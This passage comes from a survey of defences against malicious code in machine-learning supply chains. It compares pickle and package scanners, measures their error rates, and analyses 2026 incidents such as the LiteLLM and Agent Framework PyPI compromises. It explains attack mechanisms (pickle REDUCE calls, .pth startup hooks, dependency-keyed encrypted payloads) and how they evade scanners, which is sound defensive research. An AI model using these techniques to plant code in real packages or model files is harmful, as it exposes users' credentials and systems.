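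CHASE's two false alarms involved code that was insecure but harmless. One package used `exec` to read its version number from another file, which CHASE had not been given. CHASE reads only `setup.py`, `__init__.py` (which runs when a program imports the package) and the files that `__init__.py` imports. An attacker could put malicious code in a file that CHASE does not read.

### Tests of newer models

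*CASHEWS* (Noirot Ferrand, Adei and colleagues, 2026) tested more recent models on 4,884 JavaScript files, half of them malicious. GPT-5.6 Luna, an inexpensive OpenAI model, missed 7.3% of the malicious files and flagged at most one of the 2,442 benign ones. That is a very good result, but the test is too small to confirm a false-positive rate as low as 0.01%. Showing with 95% confidence that the rate is below that level would take about 30,000 benign files, even with no false alarms.

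Large files were much harder to scan. Among the 512 files with more than 25,000 tokens, Luna missed 34.9% of the malicious ones, partly because it could not process about 30% of the files and the researchers counted those as cleared. A real attack on the npm package `ai-sdk-ollama` put its malicious code in a list of more than 1.3 million numbers, which made the file 4.5 megabytes.

CASHEWS shrinks large files before a model reads them. It decodes hidden text, separates bundled modules, keeps the code that leads to sensitive operations, and shortens long names and strings. If the result is still too large, the model examines the three most suspicious parts. This reduced the share of large malicious files that Luna missed to 19.3%, but it raised the share missed across the whole collection from 7.3% to 8.0%, so the developers recommend it mainly for large files.

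*MalTotal* (2026) compared several models within one detector and found that none was consistently best across programming languages.

*LLM-Enhanced Hierarchical Heterogeneous Graph Representation Learning for Malicious Python Package Detection* (Gao, Chen and colleagues, 2026) describes a detector that builds a graph of a package's files and functions, with edges for imports and calls. A language model labels each function's role, such as reading credentials or sending data, and a smaller neural network uses the whole graph to classify the package as malicious or benign. The detector can connect an installation script with code in other files that steals data. The researchers report that it outperformed leading language models used alone.

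### How machine-learning packages fare

Many scanner rules also match routine operations in machine-learning packages. In the CHASE test, GuardDog flagged 206 of the 2,500 benign packages, or 8.2%. Toda and Mori attribute these false alarms to harmless downloads and to calls that started ordinary programs, such as the compiler `gcc` and `lscpu`, which lists processor details. A package that builds its own fast numerical code may well run both programs.

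None of these tests gives a separate false positive rate for rule-based scanners on machine-learning packages. The popular packages that Vu and colleagues scanned probably included NumPy and similar libraries, but the results do not list them separately.

The only count for such packages comes from a tool that runs the code. Jandali, Sheybani and colleagues (2026), in *Preflight*, describe how it checks a dependency for one particular program:

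1. It lists the functions from the package that the program uses.
2. A language model writes a short script that calls those functions.
3. The tool runs the script in an isolated environment and records network connections, access to secrets, files written and processes started.
4. If a suitable earlier version of the package exists, it repeats the run with that version and looks for behaviour that is new.

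Preflight cleared all 100 packages related to AI, data or machine learning that the researchers chose as benign examples. With a sample this small, the actual false positive rate could still be as high as about 3%. The result covers only the functions that the scripts called, and it does not show how a rule-based scanner would treat the same packages.

Because the results depend on which functions run, a scan can miss real attacks. Preflight cleared the compromised LiteLLM release for a program that used only LiteLLM's client functions, but flagged it for one that ran the proxy server, which contained the malicious code. Importing a compromised release of Ultralytics, an object-detection library, revealed nothing, but creating a model revealed a new network connection and a new process.

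One of Preflight's correct verdicts was partly accidental. Preflight classifies a package as malicious if it finds at least two critical behaviours. For a package called DurableTask, it counted connections to three addresses, two of which belonged to the test environment.

PyGuard and Preflight would probably also miss the yellow-square attack if it were in a dependency, because it needs no sensitive operation and creates no new connection, file or process.

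## Scanners tested on model files and the code shipped with them

Projects download trained models as well as packages, and a file of model weights can run code when a program loads it. These files are easier to check than packages in one respect, because loading weights takes only a few kinds of operation and a call to anything else stands out. The tests below all used machine-learning models or the code published with them, mostly from Hugging Face.

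### How a pickle file runs

Pickle saves a Python object as a series of instructions for rebuilding it. To load the file, Python runs an interpreter called the Pickle Machine, which follows the instructions in order. It keeps its working values on a stack, a pile where values are added and removed at the top. *SafePickle* (Ohayon, Gilkarov and Dubin, 2026) counts 68 kinds of instruction, or *opcodes*. Most of them only create or combine simple values such as numbers and text, but a few can import any installed Python function or class and call it.

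Suppose a model has one weight, named `bias`, with the value 0.5. PyTorch usually keeps weights in an `OrderedDict`, a dictionary that preserves the order of its entries. The table shows the instructions pickle would follow to rebuild this dictionary, except those that only store values for reuse.

| Instruction | What the Pickle Machine does | Stack afterwards |
|---|---|---|
| `PROTO 2` | notes the version of the format | empty |
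| `GLOBAL collections OrderedDict` | imports the class and adds it to the stack | the class |
| `EMPTY_TUPLE` | adds an empty list of arguments | the class, `()` |
| `REDUCE` | removes both, calls the class with those arguments, adds the result | an empty dictionary |
| `BINUNICODE 'bias'` | adds the text | dictionary, `'bias'` |
| `BINFLOAT 0.5` | adds the number | dictionary, `'bias'`, `0.5` |
| `SETITEM` | removes the name and number and stores them in the dictionary | `{'bias': 0.5}` |
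| `STOP` | returns the top item to the program | empty |

The risk comes from `GLOBAL` and `REDUCE`. If `GLOBAL` names `os.system`, which runs shell commands, and the argument is a command, `REDUCE` runs the command during loading, before the program uses the model.

A scanner can read the pickle instructions without executing them. From this file it would extract one import, `collections.OrderedDict`, and one call to it with no arguments. A PyTorch checkpoint is usually a ZIP archive with the pickle inside, so the scanner has to unpack the archive first.

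*PICKLEBALL* (Kellas, Li and colleagues, 2025) collected 252 benign models made with 16 libraries. For 12 of the libraries, the models used only three to five different imports and called only two of them. The other four libraries save whole Python objects along with the weights, and their models used between 18 and 63 imports.

### Lists of forbidden functions

The open-source scanners PickleScan and ModelScan compare a file's imports with a denylist of dangerous functions. Hugging Face runs versions of both on files users upload.

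Kellas and colleagues tested ModelScan on their 252 benign models and 84 malicious ones. Earlier scanners had found 82 of the malicious models on Hugging Face, and the researchers built the other two to evade detection. ModelScan caught 75 of the malicious models and flagged 16 of the benign ones (6.3%). Five of the nine attacks it missed used functions not on its list. Three others loaded the harmful part from elsewhere while running, so it was not in the file ModelScan read.

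The same test included ModelTracer, which loads the model and watches its system calls. It raised no false alarms but caught only 44 of the malicious models. Its denylist covers starting programs, opening network connections and changing file permissions, so it missed attacks that only read or wrote files.

Some functions are hard to classify as safe or dangerous. Python's `getattr` fetches part of an object by name, which an attacker can use to reach a dangerous function indirectly. But the Transformers library also uses it in the files that record a model's training settings. In *Models Are Codes*, Zhao, Hou and colleagues (2024) found 3,775 uses of `getattr` in models on Hugging Face and could not identify a malicious one. A scanner that ignores `getattr` can miss attacks that use it, but flagging it will raise many false alarms.

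A denylist would also have to cover dangerous functions in nearly every Python library. Trail of Bits' *Fickling's new AI/ML pickle file scanner* (2025) describes a malicious test file that the company uploaded to Hugging Face and that the site's scanners missed. *ShadowPickle* (Pradhan, Nambiar and Soremekun, July 2026) reports test files that evaded detection across ten scanners and four model hubs, although some scanners caught many of them.

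### Turning the file back into Python

Trail of Bits' *Never a dill moment* (2021) introduced Fickling, which decompiles a pickle into ordinary Python without loading it. For the one-weight model, the result would look roughly like this:

```python
from collections import OrderedDict
weights = OrderedDict()
weights["bias"] = 0.5
result = weights
```

An analyst can then see how the file uses a function as well as which function it imports. In one malicious sample, Fickling found an unsafe import and a variable that the rest of the program never used. Trail of Bits' *Relishing new Fickling features for securing ML systems* (2024) treats the import as much stronger evidence than the variable. The unused variable is still informative because nearly every value in a normal model file ends up in the finished object. If the program never uses a call's result, the call may be there only for its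 side effects.

Ohayon and colleagues ran Fickling on 727 files from Hugging Face, 79 of them malicious. They report that it caught 57.1% of the malicious files and flagged 14.3% of the benign ones. On the collection from Kellas and colleagues, the rates were 88.2% and 42.9%. These percentages do not correspond to whole numbers of files in either collection, so Fickling probably failed to process some files, which makes the comparison rough.

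### Lists of permitted functions

A program can enforce an allowlist in a few lines of Python by replacing the step in which the Pickle Machine looks up an import:

```python
class SafeUnpickler(pickle.Unpickler):
    def find_class(self, module, name):
        if (module, name) in ALLOWED:
            return super().find_class(module, name)
        raise pickle.UnpicklingError("import not allowed")
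```

If `ALLOWED` contains only `("collections", "OrderedDict")`, the one-weight model loads, and a file that asks for `os.system` causes an error before anything runs.

The hard part is choosing which imports to allow. Trail of Bits examined 3,000 pickle files from the most popular Hugging Face repositories and listed the imports it considered harmless. A permitted function must not be able to run code, read or change an object's attributes, import other objects or load another pickle. With this list, Fickling caught every malicious file in a test and passed 99% of the clean ones. Trail of Bits made the malicious files by inserting attacks into clean files. It does not say whether the clean files in the test were separate from the 3,000 it had used to write the list, so the false positive rate on unfamiliar models may be higher than 1%.

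PyTorch has its own allowlist, the weights-only unpickler, which has been on by default since version 2.6. In the test by Kellas and colleagues, it blocked all 84 malicious models but also 95 of the 252 benign ones, or 37.7%. All 95 came from the four libraries that save whole objects, and the unpickler loaded every benign model from the other 12.

That share is high partly because the researchers had looked for libraries with their own model classes. In a sample of 1,426 popular repositories that offered only pickle files, 219 (15.4%) contained a model that PyTorch's allowlist would block. Together these repositories had 79.6 million downloads in a month. The developers of one affected library, flair, turned the allowlist off in their loading code so that their models would still work, which leaves users without one unless they add their own.

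### An allowlist for each library

Kellas and colleagues designed PickleBall to work out what a particular library's models need. Before loading a model, it reads the library's source code and starts from the class that the model belongs to. Their example is roughly this:

```python
class Tensor:
    def __reduce__(self):
        return read_weights, (self.filename,)

class Model:
    def __init__(self, weights: Tensor):
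        self.weights = weights
```

The `__reduce__` method specifies which function pickle should call to rebuild an object, and with what arguments. PickleBall proceeds as follows:

1. `Model` has no `__reduce__` method, so PickleBall permits files to import the class. It then adds the class's subclasses and the types of its attributes to a queue. Here, that means `Tensor`.
2. `Tensor` has a `__reduce__` method that returns `read_weights`. PickleBall permits files to import and call that function, and queues the types of its arguments.
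3. The only argument is a piece of text, which needs no import. The queue is empty, so the list is complete.

PickleBall keeps separate lists for imports and calls. In the test, each library's policy permitted at least 767 imports, far more than its models used, but only 61 to 64 calls.

If a model file imports something that is not on the list, PickleBall substitutes a placeholder and raises an error only if the program tries to use it. This helps with models that contain leftovers from training, such as optimizer state, which is not needed to make predictions.

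| Defence | How it decides | Malicious models caught (of 84) | Benign models flagged or blocked (of 252) |
|---|---|---|---|
| ModelTracer | denylist of system calls | 44 | 0 |
| ModelScan | denylist of functions | 75 | 16 |
| Weights-only unpickler | one allowlist for all libraries | 84 | 95 |
| PickleBall | an allowlist for each library | 84 | 51 |

PickleBall loaded 17 of the 18 flair models, none of which worked with PyTorch's allowlist. It did worse on YOLOv11, a family of object-detection models, loading 15 of 51. Some failed because they used the name `models.common.Conv` for a class named `yolov5.models.common.Conv` in the library's source, and PickleBall did not match the two names. Others failed because they contained information that developers had attached after creating the model and that the class definition did not mention.

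The perfect detection rates warrant some caution because scanners had already found nearly all the malicious models. Kellas and colleagues also acknowledge that an attacker might combine permitted functions to do harm, although they knew of no such attack on these loaders. Ohayon and colleagues add that PickleBall trusts the library's source. If an attacker has compromised the library, PickleBall may put the attacker's function on the allowlist.

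PickleBall also takes some work to set up. Its analysis took a median of 14 seconds per library, but the researchers had to edit the source code of five of the 16 libraries before the tool could read it properly.

### A classifier that counts instructions

SafePickle, the detector that Ohayon and colleagues built, needs no list of functions. It calculates what fraction of a file's instructions belong to each opcode:

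fᵢ = nᵢ / N

Here nᵢ is the number of times opcode i occurs and N is the total number of instructions. The one-weight model has eight instructions, all with different opcodes, so each opcode's fraction is 1/8. A standard classifier, such as a random forest (a large set of decision trees whose predictions are combined), then learns which fractions are typical of malicious files.

These fractions do not record which function a file imports. Replacing `OrderedDict` with something harmful would change them little, as would adding a few instructions to a file with thousands. Ohayon and colleagues say they have yet to test deliberate manipulation of the fractions.

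The table shows their results on their own collection and on the one from Kellas and colleagues. They trained the random forest only on their own collection.

| Tool | Own collection: caught | Own collection: benign flagged | Kellas collection: caught | Kellas collection: benign flagged |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| PickleScan | 97.5% | 100% | 97.2% | 7.5% |
| ModelScan | 100% | 100% | 100% | 100% |
| SafePickle (random forest) | 87.5% | 3.1% | 93.0% | 39.2% |
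| PickleBall | not tested | not tested | 100% | 20.2% |

SafePickle had the best balance on familiar data, but that test seems to have included only 16 malicious files, of which it caught 14. On the other collection, it flagged nearly two in five benign files, about twice as many as PickleBall. The paper reports F1 scores on that collection of 81.22 for SafePickle and 76.09 for PickleBall. But SafePickle's rates in the table imply about 76 correct alarms and 100 false ones, which gives an F1 score of about 59.

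The results for ModelScan depend heavily on how detections are counted. Ohayon and colleagues counted any issue that ModelScan reported as a detection, and found that it flagged every benign file. Kellas and colleagues found that it flagged 6.3% of almost the same files. PickleScan's false positive rate also differed sharply between the two collections. A team choosing a scanner would therefore learn more from testing scanners on the models it uses than from either set of published rates.

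SafePickle detected all nine malicious files that the researchers had disguised by wrapping them in various archive and compression formats, while the other scanners mostly failed to read them. It also detected five real malicious files, compared with four for PickleScan and one for Fickling. Neither test included benign files.

*Detecting AI Pickling* (Nice, 2026), published by the SANS Institute, a security training organisation, compares PickleScan, ModelScan and Fickling with a check based on `pickletools`, Python's module for listing a pickle's instructions. Nice tested them on clean and poisoned models saved in three common formats. Some tools flagged too many clean models, and others missed poisoned ones in particular formats. Nice concludes that a company should not rely on any single tool to decide which models to accept.

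### Scanning an entire hub

Zhao and colleagues built MalHug to find malicious models on Hugging Face and to examine what their code does. It also covers Keras, a neural-network library that lets developers put a Python function inside a model as a *Lambda layer*. In the older HDF5 file format, the layer contains compiled Python code, so loading or using the model can run whatever its author wrote. MalHug works as follows:

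1. It lists the instructions in each pickle and searches for opcodes that can import or call functions.
2. If it finds a suspicious call, it uses Fickling to decompile the file and extracts any code in the call's arguments. In one model, an argument contained a complete Python script.
3. For Keras models, it extracts the Lambda layers and decompiles them.
4. It applies taint analysis to the extracted code. For example, it checks whether the names or settings of the user's computer can reach a web request.
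5. It searches for known patterns of shell commands and disguised code with YARA, a tool for writing malware signatures.

It applies the last two steps to dataset loading scripts as well.

MalHug ran for more than three months on a copy of Hugging Face at Ant Group, a Chinese financial technology company. It scanned 705,991 models and 176,386 datasets, totaling 179.4 terabytes, and found 91 malicious models and nine malicious loading scripts. Some models gave an outsider remote control of the computer that loaded them. One dataset script stole passwords and cookies from the Chrome browser. Some of the 100 were harmless demonstrations by security researchers, not real attacks.

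The results support the idea that harmful operations stand out in model files. Apart from `getattr`, the functions that Zhao and colleagues list as dangerous appeared only 78 times in pickle models across the hub, and MalHug found 76 malicious pickle models. The hub had 72 Lambda layers, and 15 malicious models used them. These rare operations were therefore a strong reason to inspect a file, unlike `getattr`, which was common and gave almost no evidence of harm.

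Even so, a scanner's error rate matters a lot at this scale. About 573,000 of the model repositories contained files. At the rates Kellas and colleagues measured, ModelScan would catch about 81 of the 91 malicious models and raise about 36,000 false alarms. The real number of false alarms might be lower, because their test contained an unusually large share of complicated models.

The number of malicious models MalHug missed is unknown because Zhao and colleagues had no labelled collection to test it on. They note that attackers could disguise code in ways MalHug does not recognise.

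### Files that contain only data

The simplest way to stop a model file from running code is to use a format that has no instruction for calling functions. Hugging Face released *safetensors* in 2022 for this purpose. A safetensors file stores the weights and a description of their names, types and shapes. For the one-weight model, the file would contain the name `bias` and the number 0.5. It would not mention `OrderedDict`, because the loading program decides how to store the weights.

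Malware scanners have little to look for in safetensors files, and none of the tests above gives a detection rate for them. Kellas and colleagues consider the format secure because it needs few operations and has passed independent security audits. A safetensors file cannot specify a function to run, though a bug in the program that loads it could still cause problems.

Many projects have not completely switched from pickle to safetensors. In March 2025, about 44.9% of the popular Hugging Face repositories that Kellas and colleagues examined still contained pickle models, and 21% contained only pickle models. Developers often keep the pickle version next to the safetensors one for older programs. A fine-tuned model can also have its weights in safetensors but come with a pickle file of its training settings.

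Weights stored in a data-only format can still be untrustworthy. If someone trains a clothing classifier on the yellow-square labels, the resulting weights are ordinary numbers, and safetensors will store them like any others. Kellas and colleagues likewise say that PickleBall is not meant to prevent backdoors in the weights.

### When the model needs its own code

Safetensors files do not store a model's architecture code. For common designs, libraries such as Transformers already include this code. A new design may have features the library lacks, such as a different way of encoding each word's position, so its developers publish Python code with the model, and users have to set `trust_remote_code=True` to run it.

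*An Empirical Study on Remote Code Execution in Machine Learning Model Hosting* (Siddiq, Romel and colleagues, 2026) examined this practice on five model hubs. On Hugging Face, 36,697 of about 2.1 million repositories (1.74%) contained custom code, including those of important models such as DeepSeek-R1. On two much smaller hubs, OpenMMLab and PyTorch Hub, every repository had custom code.

Repositories often contain scripts that have nothing to do with loading the model. The researchers therefore built a call graph from the files that start the loading process and kept only the code it could reach. This reduced 128,487 Python files to 67,009. They then ran four general analysers on the remaining code, with these results for Hugging Face:

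| Analyser | Repositories flagged | Most common alert | Share of that tool's alerts |
|---|---|---|---|
| Bandit | 7.70% | use of `assert` | 78.2% |
| Semgrep | 4.60% | NumPy used in PyTorch code in a way that may involve pickle | 42.3% |
| CodeQL | 5.16% | comparison that might reveal a secret through its timing | 98.5% |
| YARA | 6.98% | signature of a 3D-drawing file format | 82.5% |

Most of these alerts are weak evidence of malice. An `assert` statement checks a condition, such as whether two tensors have matching shapes, and is normal in research code. The timing rule is meant for code that compares passwords or keys, but many of its alerts probably come from language-model code that compares "tokens", as happened with Bandit's password rule in the earlier survey of training projects. The 3D-drawing signature presumably matched by chance, since the researchers were scanning Python code.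 YARA's next most common alerts were for virtual-machine checks, which malware sometimes uses to avoid analysts, but Siddiq and colleagues found no clear evidence of embedded malware in YARA's results.

PickleScan, ModelScan and two other scanners for malicious model files found nothing in the code that runs during loading. This does not show that the code was safe, because the scanners mainly examine saved model files rather than Python source.

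Custom code is harder to check than pickle files because a short allowlist would block much of what it needs. A file such as `modeling_example.py` may legitimately read settings, download more files or compile a fast routine for a graphics processor. Reviewers face the same problem with any Python package. As of October 2025, none of the five hubs ran custom code in an isolated environment during loading, and only Hugging Face automatically scanned every upload.

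Siddiq and colleagues describe an attack in which someone copies a legitimate model, adds harmful code to its loading script and publishes the result as an improved version. This attack would be easier to find by comparing the copy with the original, because the loading scripts would differ even if the weights were identical and safely stored in safetensors.

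## What live monitoring and known incidents show

A scanner that checks new releases as they arrive faces a more realistic mix than any labelled collection, because nobody has chosen how many are malicious. In *One Detector Fits All*, Montaruli, Compagna and colleagues (2025) ran the same detector over 37 days in the spring of 2025 for two kinds of user: a PyPI administrator who checks every upload, and a large software company that checks only its own dependencies. Two of the researchers work at the software company SAP. The packages were general Python software, with no separate results for machine learning.

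### One detector, two thresholds

For each release, the detector counts calls to 215 security-sensitive functions, measures how random the text in the code looks, and counts suspicious sequences of operations. A large set of decision trees combines these numbers into a score, and the user chooses the threshold for raising an alarm. The researchers name each threshold after its false positive rate on PyPI.

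The table shows results for 91,949 releases of 38,567 PyPI packages. Of those releases, 216 were known to be malicious. The last column is for the company, which had 1,596 releases to check from 584 dependencies.

| Setting | Malicious releases caught on PyPI | False alarms on PyPI | Precision on PyPI | False alarms at the company |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 30% | 208 | 27,478 | 0.8% | 130 |
| 10% | 196 | 9,152 | 2.1% | 46 |
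| 1% | 180 | 781 | 18.7% | 2 |
| 0.1% | 92 | 81 | 53.2% | 0 |

For PyPI, the researchers chose the 0.1% setting, which found about 2.5 malicious releases and raised about 2.2 false alarms a day, but missed 124 of the 216 malicious releases. The company used the 10% setting and had 1.24 false alarms a day.

PyPI's administrators and the company chose differently mainly because PyPI received about 2,500 releases a day, while the company's dependencies produced about 43. At the company's setting, PyPI's administrators would have had to read about 247 false alarms every day. Missed attacks also concern the company more, because its own passwords and customers are at risk.

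At a minute per alarm, the 0.1% setting requires about 33 minutes of review a week, including about 15 minutes for false alarms. Montaruli and colleagues argue that this setting fits the 20 minutes a week that a PyPI administrator had been willing to spend on malware reports, but it fits only if the correct alarms aren't counted. The false positive rate is also nearly nine times the 0.01% that PyPI's administrators had already considered too high.

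The company's result measures only workload. None of its dependencies was attacked during the 37 days, so nobody knows what the detector would have caught there. The researchers expected it to catch about 90%, as it did on PyPI at the same setting. That figure may not hold for a hijacked release of a well-known library, where a few malicious files sit among hundreds of legitimate ones and barely change the package's overall counts.

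Live results were also worse than laboratory results. At the 1% setting, an earlier version of the detector caught about 96% of the malicious packages in a labelled collection but only 69% in a live stream from late 2024. Adding that stream to the training data helped, and the final version caught 83% in the spring.

### Code that runs before the program

In three attacks on Python packages in the autumn of 2026, the malicious code ran every time Python started, even if the user's program never imported the package that had brought it in. Park (2026), in the Korean-language *LiteLLM v1.107.0 공급망 공격*, explains the mechanism, known as a *startup hook*. When Python starts, a built-in module called `site` looks through `site-packages`, the folder where the installer `pip` puts packages. Two kinds of file there can run code:

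- A `.pth` file normally lists extra folders in which Python should look for modules. If a line starts with `import`, Python executes it.
- Python imports a file called `sitecustomize.py` automatically if it finds one. Administrators can use it to adjust settings for every program on a machine.

Suppose a team keeps the ten-line training loop in `train.py`, and somebody has installed a package with both kinds of hook in the same environment. This happens when the team starts a training run:

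1. Python starts and `site` opens `cook.pth`, which contains only `import cook`. The code in `cook.py` runs.
2. `site` imports `sitecustomize.py`, and its code runs.
3. Python reads the first line of `train.py`.

An analyser that starts at `train.py` and follows its imports will reach PyTorch and everything PyTorch imports, but not `cook.py`, because no file in the project or in PyTorch mentions it. Reading the modules of the package that installed the hook may not help, since that package does not have to import the file. CHASE could miss such a hook because it does not read every file in a package.

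A tool can find hooks by listing every `.pth` file and `sitecustomize.py` in the environment. It would need an allowlist because some legitimate packages use them too. For example, Setuptools, a standard packaging library, has installed a `.pth` file with an `import` line.

### LiteLLM 1.107.0

On 21 October 2026, LiteLLM's official release pipeline published a version that stole credentials. It was the project's second compromise of the year. Wang (2026), in *The attack chain behind the v1.107.0 LiteLLM release*, gives the company's own account of the cause, and The Hacker News' *Leaked LiteLLM Master Key Let Attackers Steal GitHub Tokens* (2026) adds exact times:

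| Time (UTC) | Event |
|---|---|
| 27 May | A LiteLLM developer accidentally publishes the master key to an internal tool. The team removes the file but does not revoke the key. |
| 10 October | The attacker uses the key to steal an access token that belongs to the owner of LiteLLM's GitHub organisation, and then the tokens of two engineers. |
| 21 October, 10:08–11:08 | The attacker overrides GitHub's protections and makes the release pipeline take its source from `Berri-AI/litellm` instead of `BerriAI/litellm`. |
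| 11:39 | The pipeline publishes version 1.107.0 on PyPI. |
| 12:06 | Lidor Machluf, a researcher at the security company Upwind, reports the attack. |
| Shortly before 13:00 | LiteLLM's team becomes aware of it. |
| 13:23 | PyPI quarantines the release. |
| 14:20 | LiteLLM finishes removing the affected images from Docker Hub, which distributes ready-to-run copies of software. |

An outsider noticed within 27 minutes of publication, and the release was available on PyPI for an hour and 44 minutes. By then the attacker had held the owner's token for 11 days.

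The foreign code was easy to separate from the rest. Singh (2026), in *Compromised LiteLLM 1.107.0 on PyPI Installs a Credential Stealer and Backdoor*, found three added files in the release: `cook.pth`, `cook.py` and `sitecustomize.py`. The first two collected login keys, cloud credentials, browser passwords and the keys that LiteLLM's server stores for language-model providers. The third contacted the attacker every hour for more code to run. The attacker had added them with one line in the settings for maturin, the tool that builds the package:

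```toml
[tool.maturin]
python-source = "."
data = "cook"        # copies the folder "cook" into the release
```

Singh compared the release with LiteLLM's public history and found no commit containing this line or the folder. The commit LiteLLM had labelled 1.107.0 contained the version number 1.108.0, and the published source matched a later commit better. Five files still differed from that later commit. Four differed by a harmless line that also appears in clean releases, and the fifth contained the attacker's change.

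The copy a reviewer examined also mattered. PyPI offered both a source archive and ready-to-install wheels, and the archive left out the `cook` folder. A reviewer who read only the archive would have had to notice a single configuration line. A scanner that read every file in a wheel would have had much more evidence, because `cook.py` decoded and unpacked a long piece of text, then ran it with `exec`, a standard pattern in scanner rules.

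Signatures did not help because the genuine pipeline had built and signed the release, which made its signature and origin look correct (Cornelißen, 2026, *LiteLLM 1.107.0 war ein Credential-Stealer*). LiteLLM had strengthened that pipeline after the first attack of the year. According to Park, it had moved releases to a separate repository, adopted trusted publishing and started signing its images. The October attacker ran the unmodified pipeline on different source code.

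The clearest warning before publication was in GitHub's account records. Wang writes that the attacker first tried and failed to get the pipeline change approved normally, then used the owner's token to bypass the restrictions. An alert for that event could have reached the team at least half an hour before the release existed. Publishing normally also requires approval from a special account on a physical device in LiteLLM's office. That week, the company had relaxed the rule to let any two engineers approve a release, and the attacker had two engineers' tokens. Wang acknowledges that the attacker could have used the owner's token to remove the rule anyway.

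Users could have avoided the release without detecting anything. Cornelißen recommends pinning exact versions in a lock file and waiting a few days before installing new ones. The delay works only if someone else examines the release in the meantime, as Upwind did here.

This fast response still came too late for many users. In *Popular AI tool LiteLLM says unrevoked key allowed hackers to target users*, Martin (2026) cites the security company Wiz's figure of about 49,000 downloads. Park notes that this figure includes automatic copies by mirrors and build systems, so it is not a count of infected machines. About four and a half hours after the upload, the attacker was already testing which AI models the stolen Amazon cloud credentials gave access to.

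Early accounts of an incident can be wrong. Within two days of the attack, Park and Cornelißen repeated LiteLLM's first theory, that the attacker had found the tokens in the logs of an exposed server. LiteLLM's investigation later traced the tokens to the key from May.

### An earlier attack with a bug in it

Attackers published two malicious versions of LiteLLM on 24 March. According to Snyk's *How a Poisoned Security Scanner Became the Key to Backdooring LiteLLM*, they got the publishing credentials through a compromised copy of Trivy, a security scanner that LiteLLM ran in its build system. PyPI quarantined the releases after about three hours.

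That attack was discovered because of a programming mistake. The blog post *anatomy of a supply chain attack litellm on pypi* explains that the malware's startup hook started a second Python process. That process also ran the hook and started a third, and so on until the computer ran out of memory. Somebody investigated the crash and found the malware.

The March attack might have lasted longer without this bug. The backdoor in October's release held a lock file, which programs commonly use to prevent more than one copy of a process from running at a time. If the lock file served that purpose, the same accident would not have exposed the backdoor.

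### Microsoft Agent Framework

Less than a month after the second LiteLLM attack, attackers hijacked the official PyPI package for Microsoft Agent Framework, a toolkit for building AI agents. Aikido's *Two malicious agent-framework releases hit PyPI in 33 minutes* describes versions 1.26.1 and 1.26.2, which appeared on 17 November. Both contained code that ran every time Python started and stole secrets for Microsoft's Azure cloud and automated build systems. Fadilpašić (2026) also reported the attack in *Microsoft's official Agent Framework Python package on PyPI hijacked*.

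The releases were available for about 45 minutes, from 20:35 to roughly 21:20 UTC, so somebody must have noticed within that time. The package has about 190,000 downloads a month, or about 200 in an average 45 minutes. Many of those would be automated builds, which often install the newest version that the project's settings allow. A requirement of `agent-framework>=1.26` would have allowed either malicious release to be installed without anyone approving it.

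A comparison with version 1.26.0 would probably have made the added code obvious. The hijacked package is a *meta-package*, which mainly installs other packages, so it normally needs little code of its own and does not need to read cloud credentials. The timing also favours automatic checks, because a person who checked new releases once a day would most likely have missed the whole incident.

### Packages that use other packages as a key

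The third case was designed to defeat scanners that test one package at a time. The Hacker News' *8 Malicious PyPI Packages Use Python Dependencies as Keys* (2026) reports on eight packages that researchers at the security company Island linked to one campaign. They call its technique *DevGating*. The latest pair of packages, `mailreader` and `confext`, came from two different PyPI accounts and worked roughly like this:

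1. `mailreader` contains a working program for reading email. It also contains a file called `default.config`, which looks like a settings file but is really a pickle with malicious code inside.
2. `mailreader` asks `confext` to read its settings. `confext` loads whatever pickle file it receives, which runs the hidden code.
3. The code checks whether the running program has already loaded a particular part of `requests`, a very common library for web requests.
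4. If so, it uses the name of that module to work out the key that decrypts the main payload. Otherwise, it does nothing harmful.
5. The payload installs a `.pth` file, so it runs again at every Python start, even after the user uninstalls the package. It then downloads further code, which the attacker can change at any time.

This is a logic bomb, but it is harder to read than those in the Android experiments because the guarded code is encrypted. A static tool would have to recover the key before it could examine that code, whereas an analyser in the Android experiments could examine both sides of a condition without knowing whether the condition would ever hold.

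Running the package as a test may also fail. If a scanner installs `mailreader` in an empty environment and imports it, nothing happens because `requests` has not been loaded. A developer's program may well import `requests` first, and many machine-learning projects load it to download models and data.

Several checks could still have found the attack. A pickle scanner would have had a good chance if it had identified `default.config` by its contents instead of its name, since a settings file does not need to import and call functions. A dynamic test could have found the attack by loading common libraries before the suspect package. A tool that compared the `.pth` files in an environment before and after a program ran would have found the new one, regardless of what created it.

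Island dates the start of the campaign to 25 September, about ten weeks before the news report of 3 December. The attackers released the packages in four waves and improved their disguise each time, so the ten weeks are not the lifetime of any single package. All eight packages are small, general tools that any Python project might install, and none imitates a machine-learning library.

### Attacks that nobody noticed

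The malicious LiteLLM and Agent Framework releases stayed on PyPI for between about 45 minutes and three hours. These times don't show how long malicious releases usually last, because they exclude attacks that nobody has found yet. The known attacks are also the easiest kind to find, because they involved popular packages and stole secrets or fetched more code, which leaves new files and network connections for researchers to investigate. A changed loss function leaves neither, so a lack of public incidents is weak evidence that such changes are rare.

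A list of incidents cannot give a rate, because it leaves out the clean releases. Live monitoring counts those, but its results still depend on which attacks people have recognised. Montaruli and colleagues took their 216 malicious releases from two public databases and from their own checks of the detector's alarms. If the databases and the checks both missed another 100 malicious releases, the detector would have caught 92 out of 316 at the 0.1% setting, or 29%, instead of 43%. The same uncertainty applies to the live runs of PyGuard and MalHug, which counted only what each tool found.

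The 216 cases amount to about one malicious release in 426 on PyPI, which is best read as a minimum. The rate among the packages a particular team uses may be very different. The company in the same study had no known attack in 1,596 releases. If each release had the same independent risk, that result would still fit a rate as high as about one in 530.

### Tampering by an insider

Outsiders carried out the package attacks, but people with legitimate access can interfere with training directly. In October 2024, ByteDance, the Chinese company behind TikTok, confirmed that an intern had maliciously interfered with model training in one of its research projects. The company said it had dismissed the intern in August and that the interference had not affected its commercial products or its large language models.

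ByteDance sued the former intern in Beijing the following month. According to Reuters, it demanded 8 million yuan (about $1.1 million) and alleged that the intern had deliberately sabotaged the team's training by manipulating code and making unauthorised changes. Chinese press reports dated the interference to June and July. The intern reportedly denied responsibility and told others that someone else had altered the code. This account is based on the company's statements and press reports, not a court's findings.

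Rumours spread on Chinese social media that the damage was much greater, with more than 8,000 graphics processors disrupted and tens of millions of dollars lost. ByteDance called such claims seriously exaggerated. Some posts also said that code hidden in a checkpoint had changed other people's optimizers and paused their programs at random. The posts do not prove this, but it is technically plausible if the checkpoint was a pickle file.

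Code that an employee adds to a colleague's project without permission is non-native, because the people who run the project have not accepted it. A provenance check might still pass it if the check verifies only that the change came from somebody inside the company. Requiring a second person's approval would help with changes to the repository, but not with a modified library on a shared machine. The team could detect a modified library by comparing the installed files with the official release.

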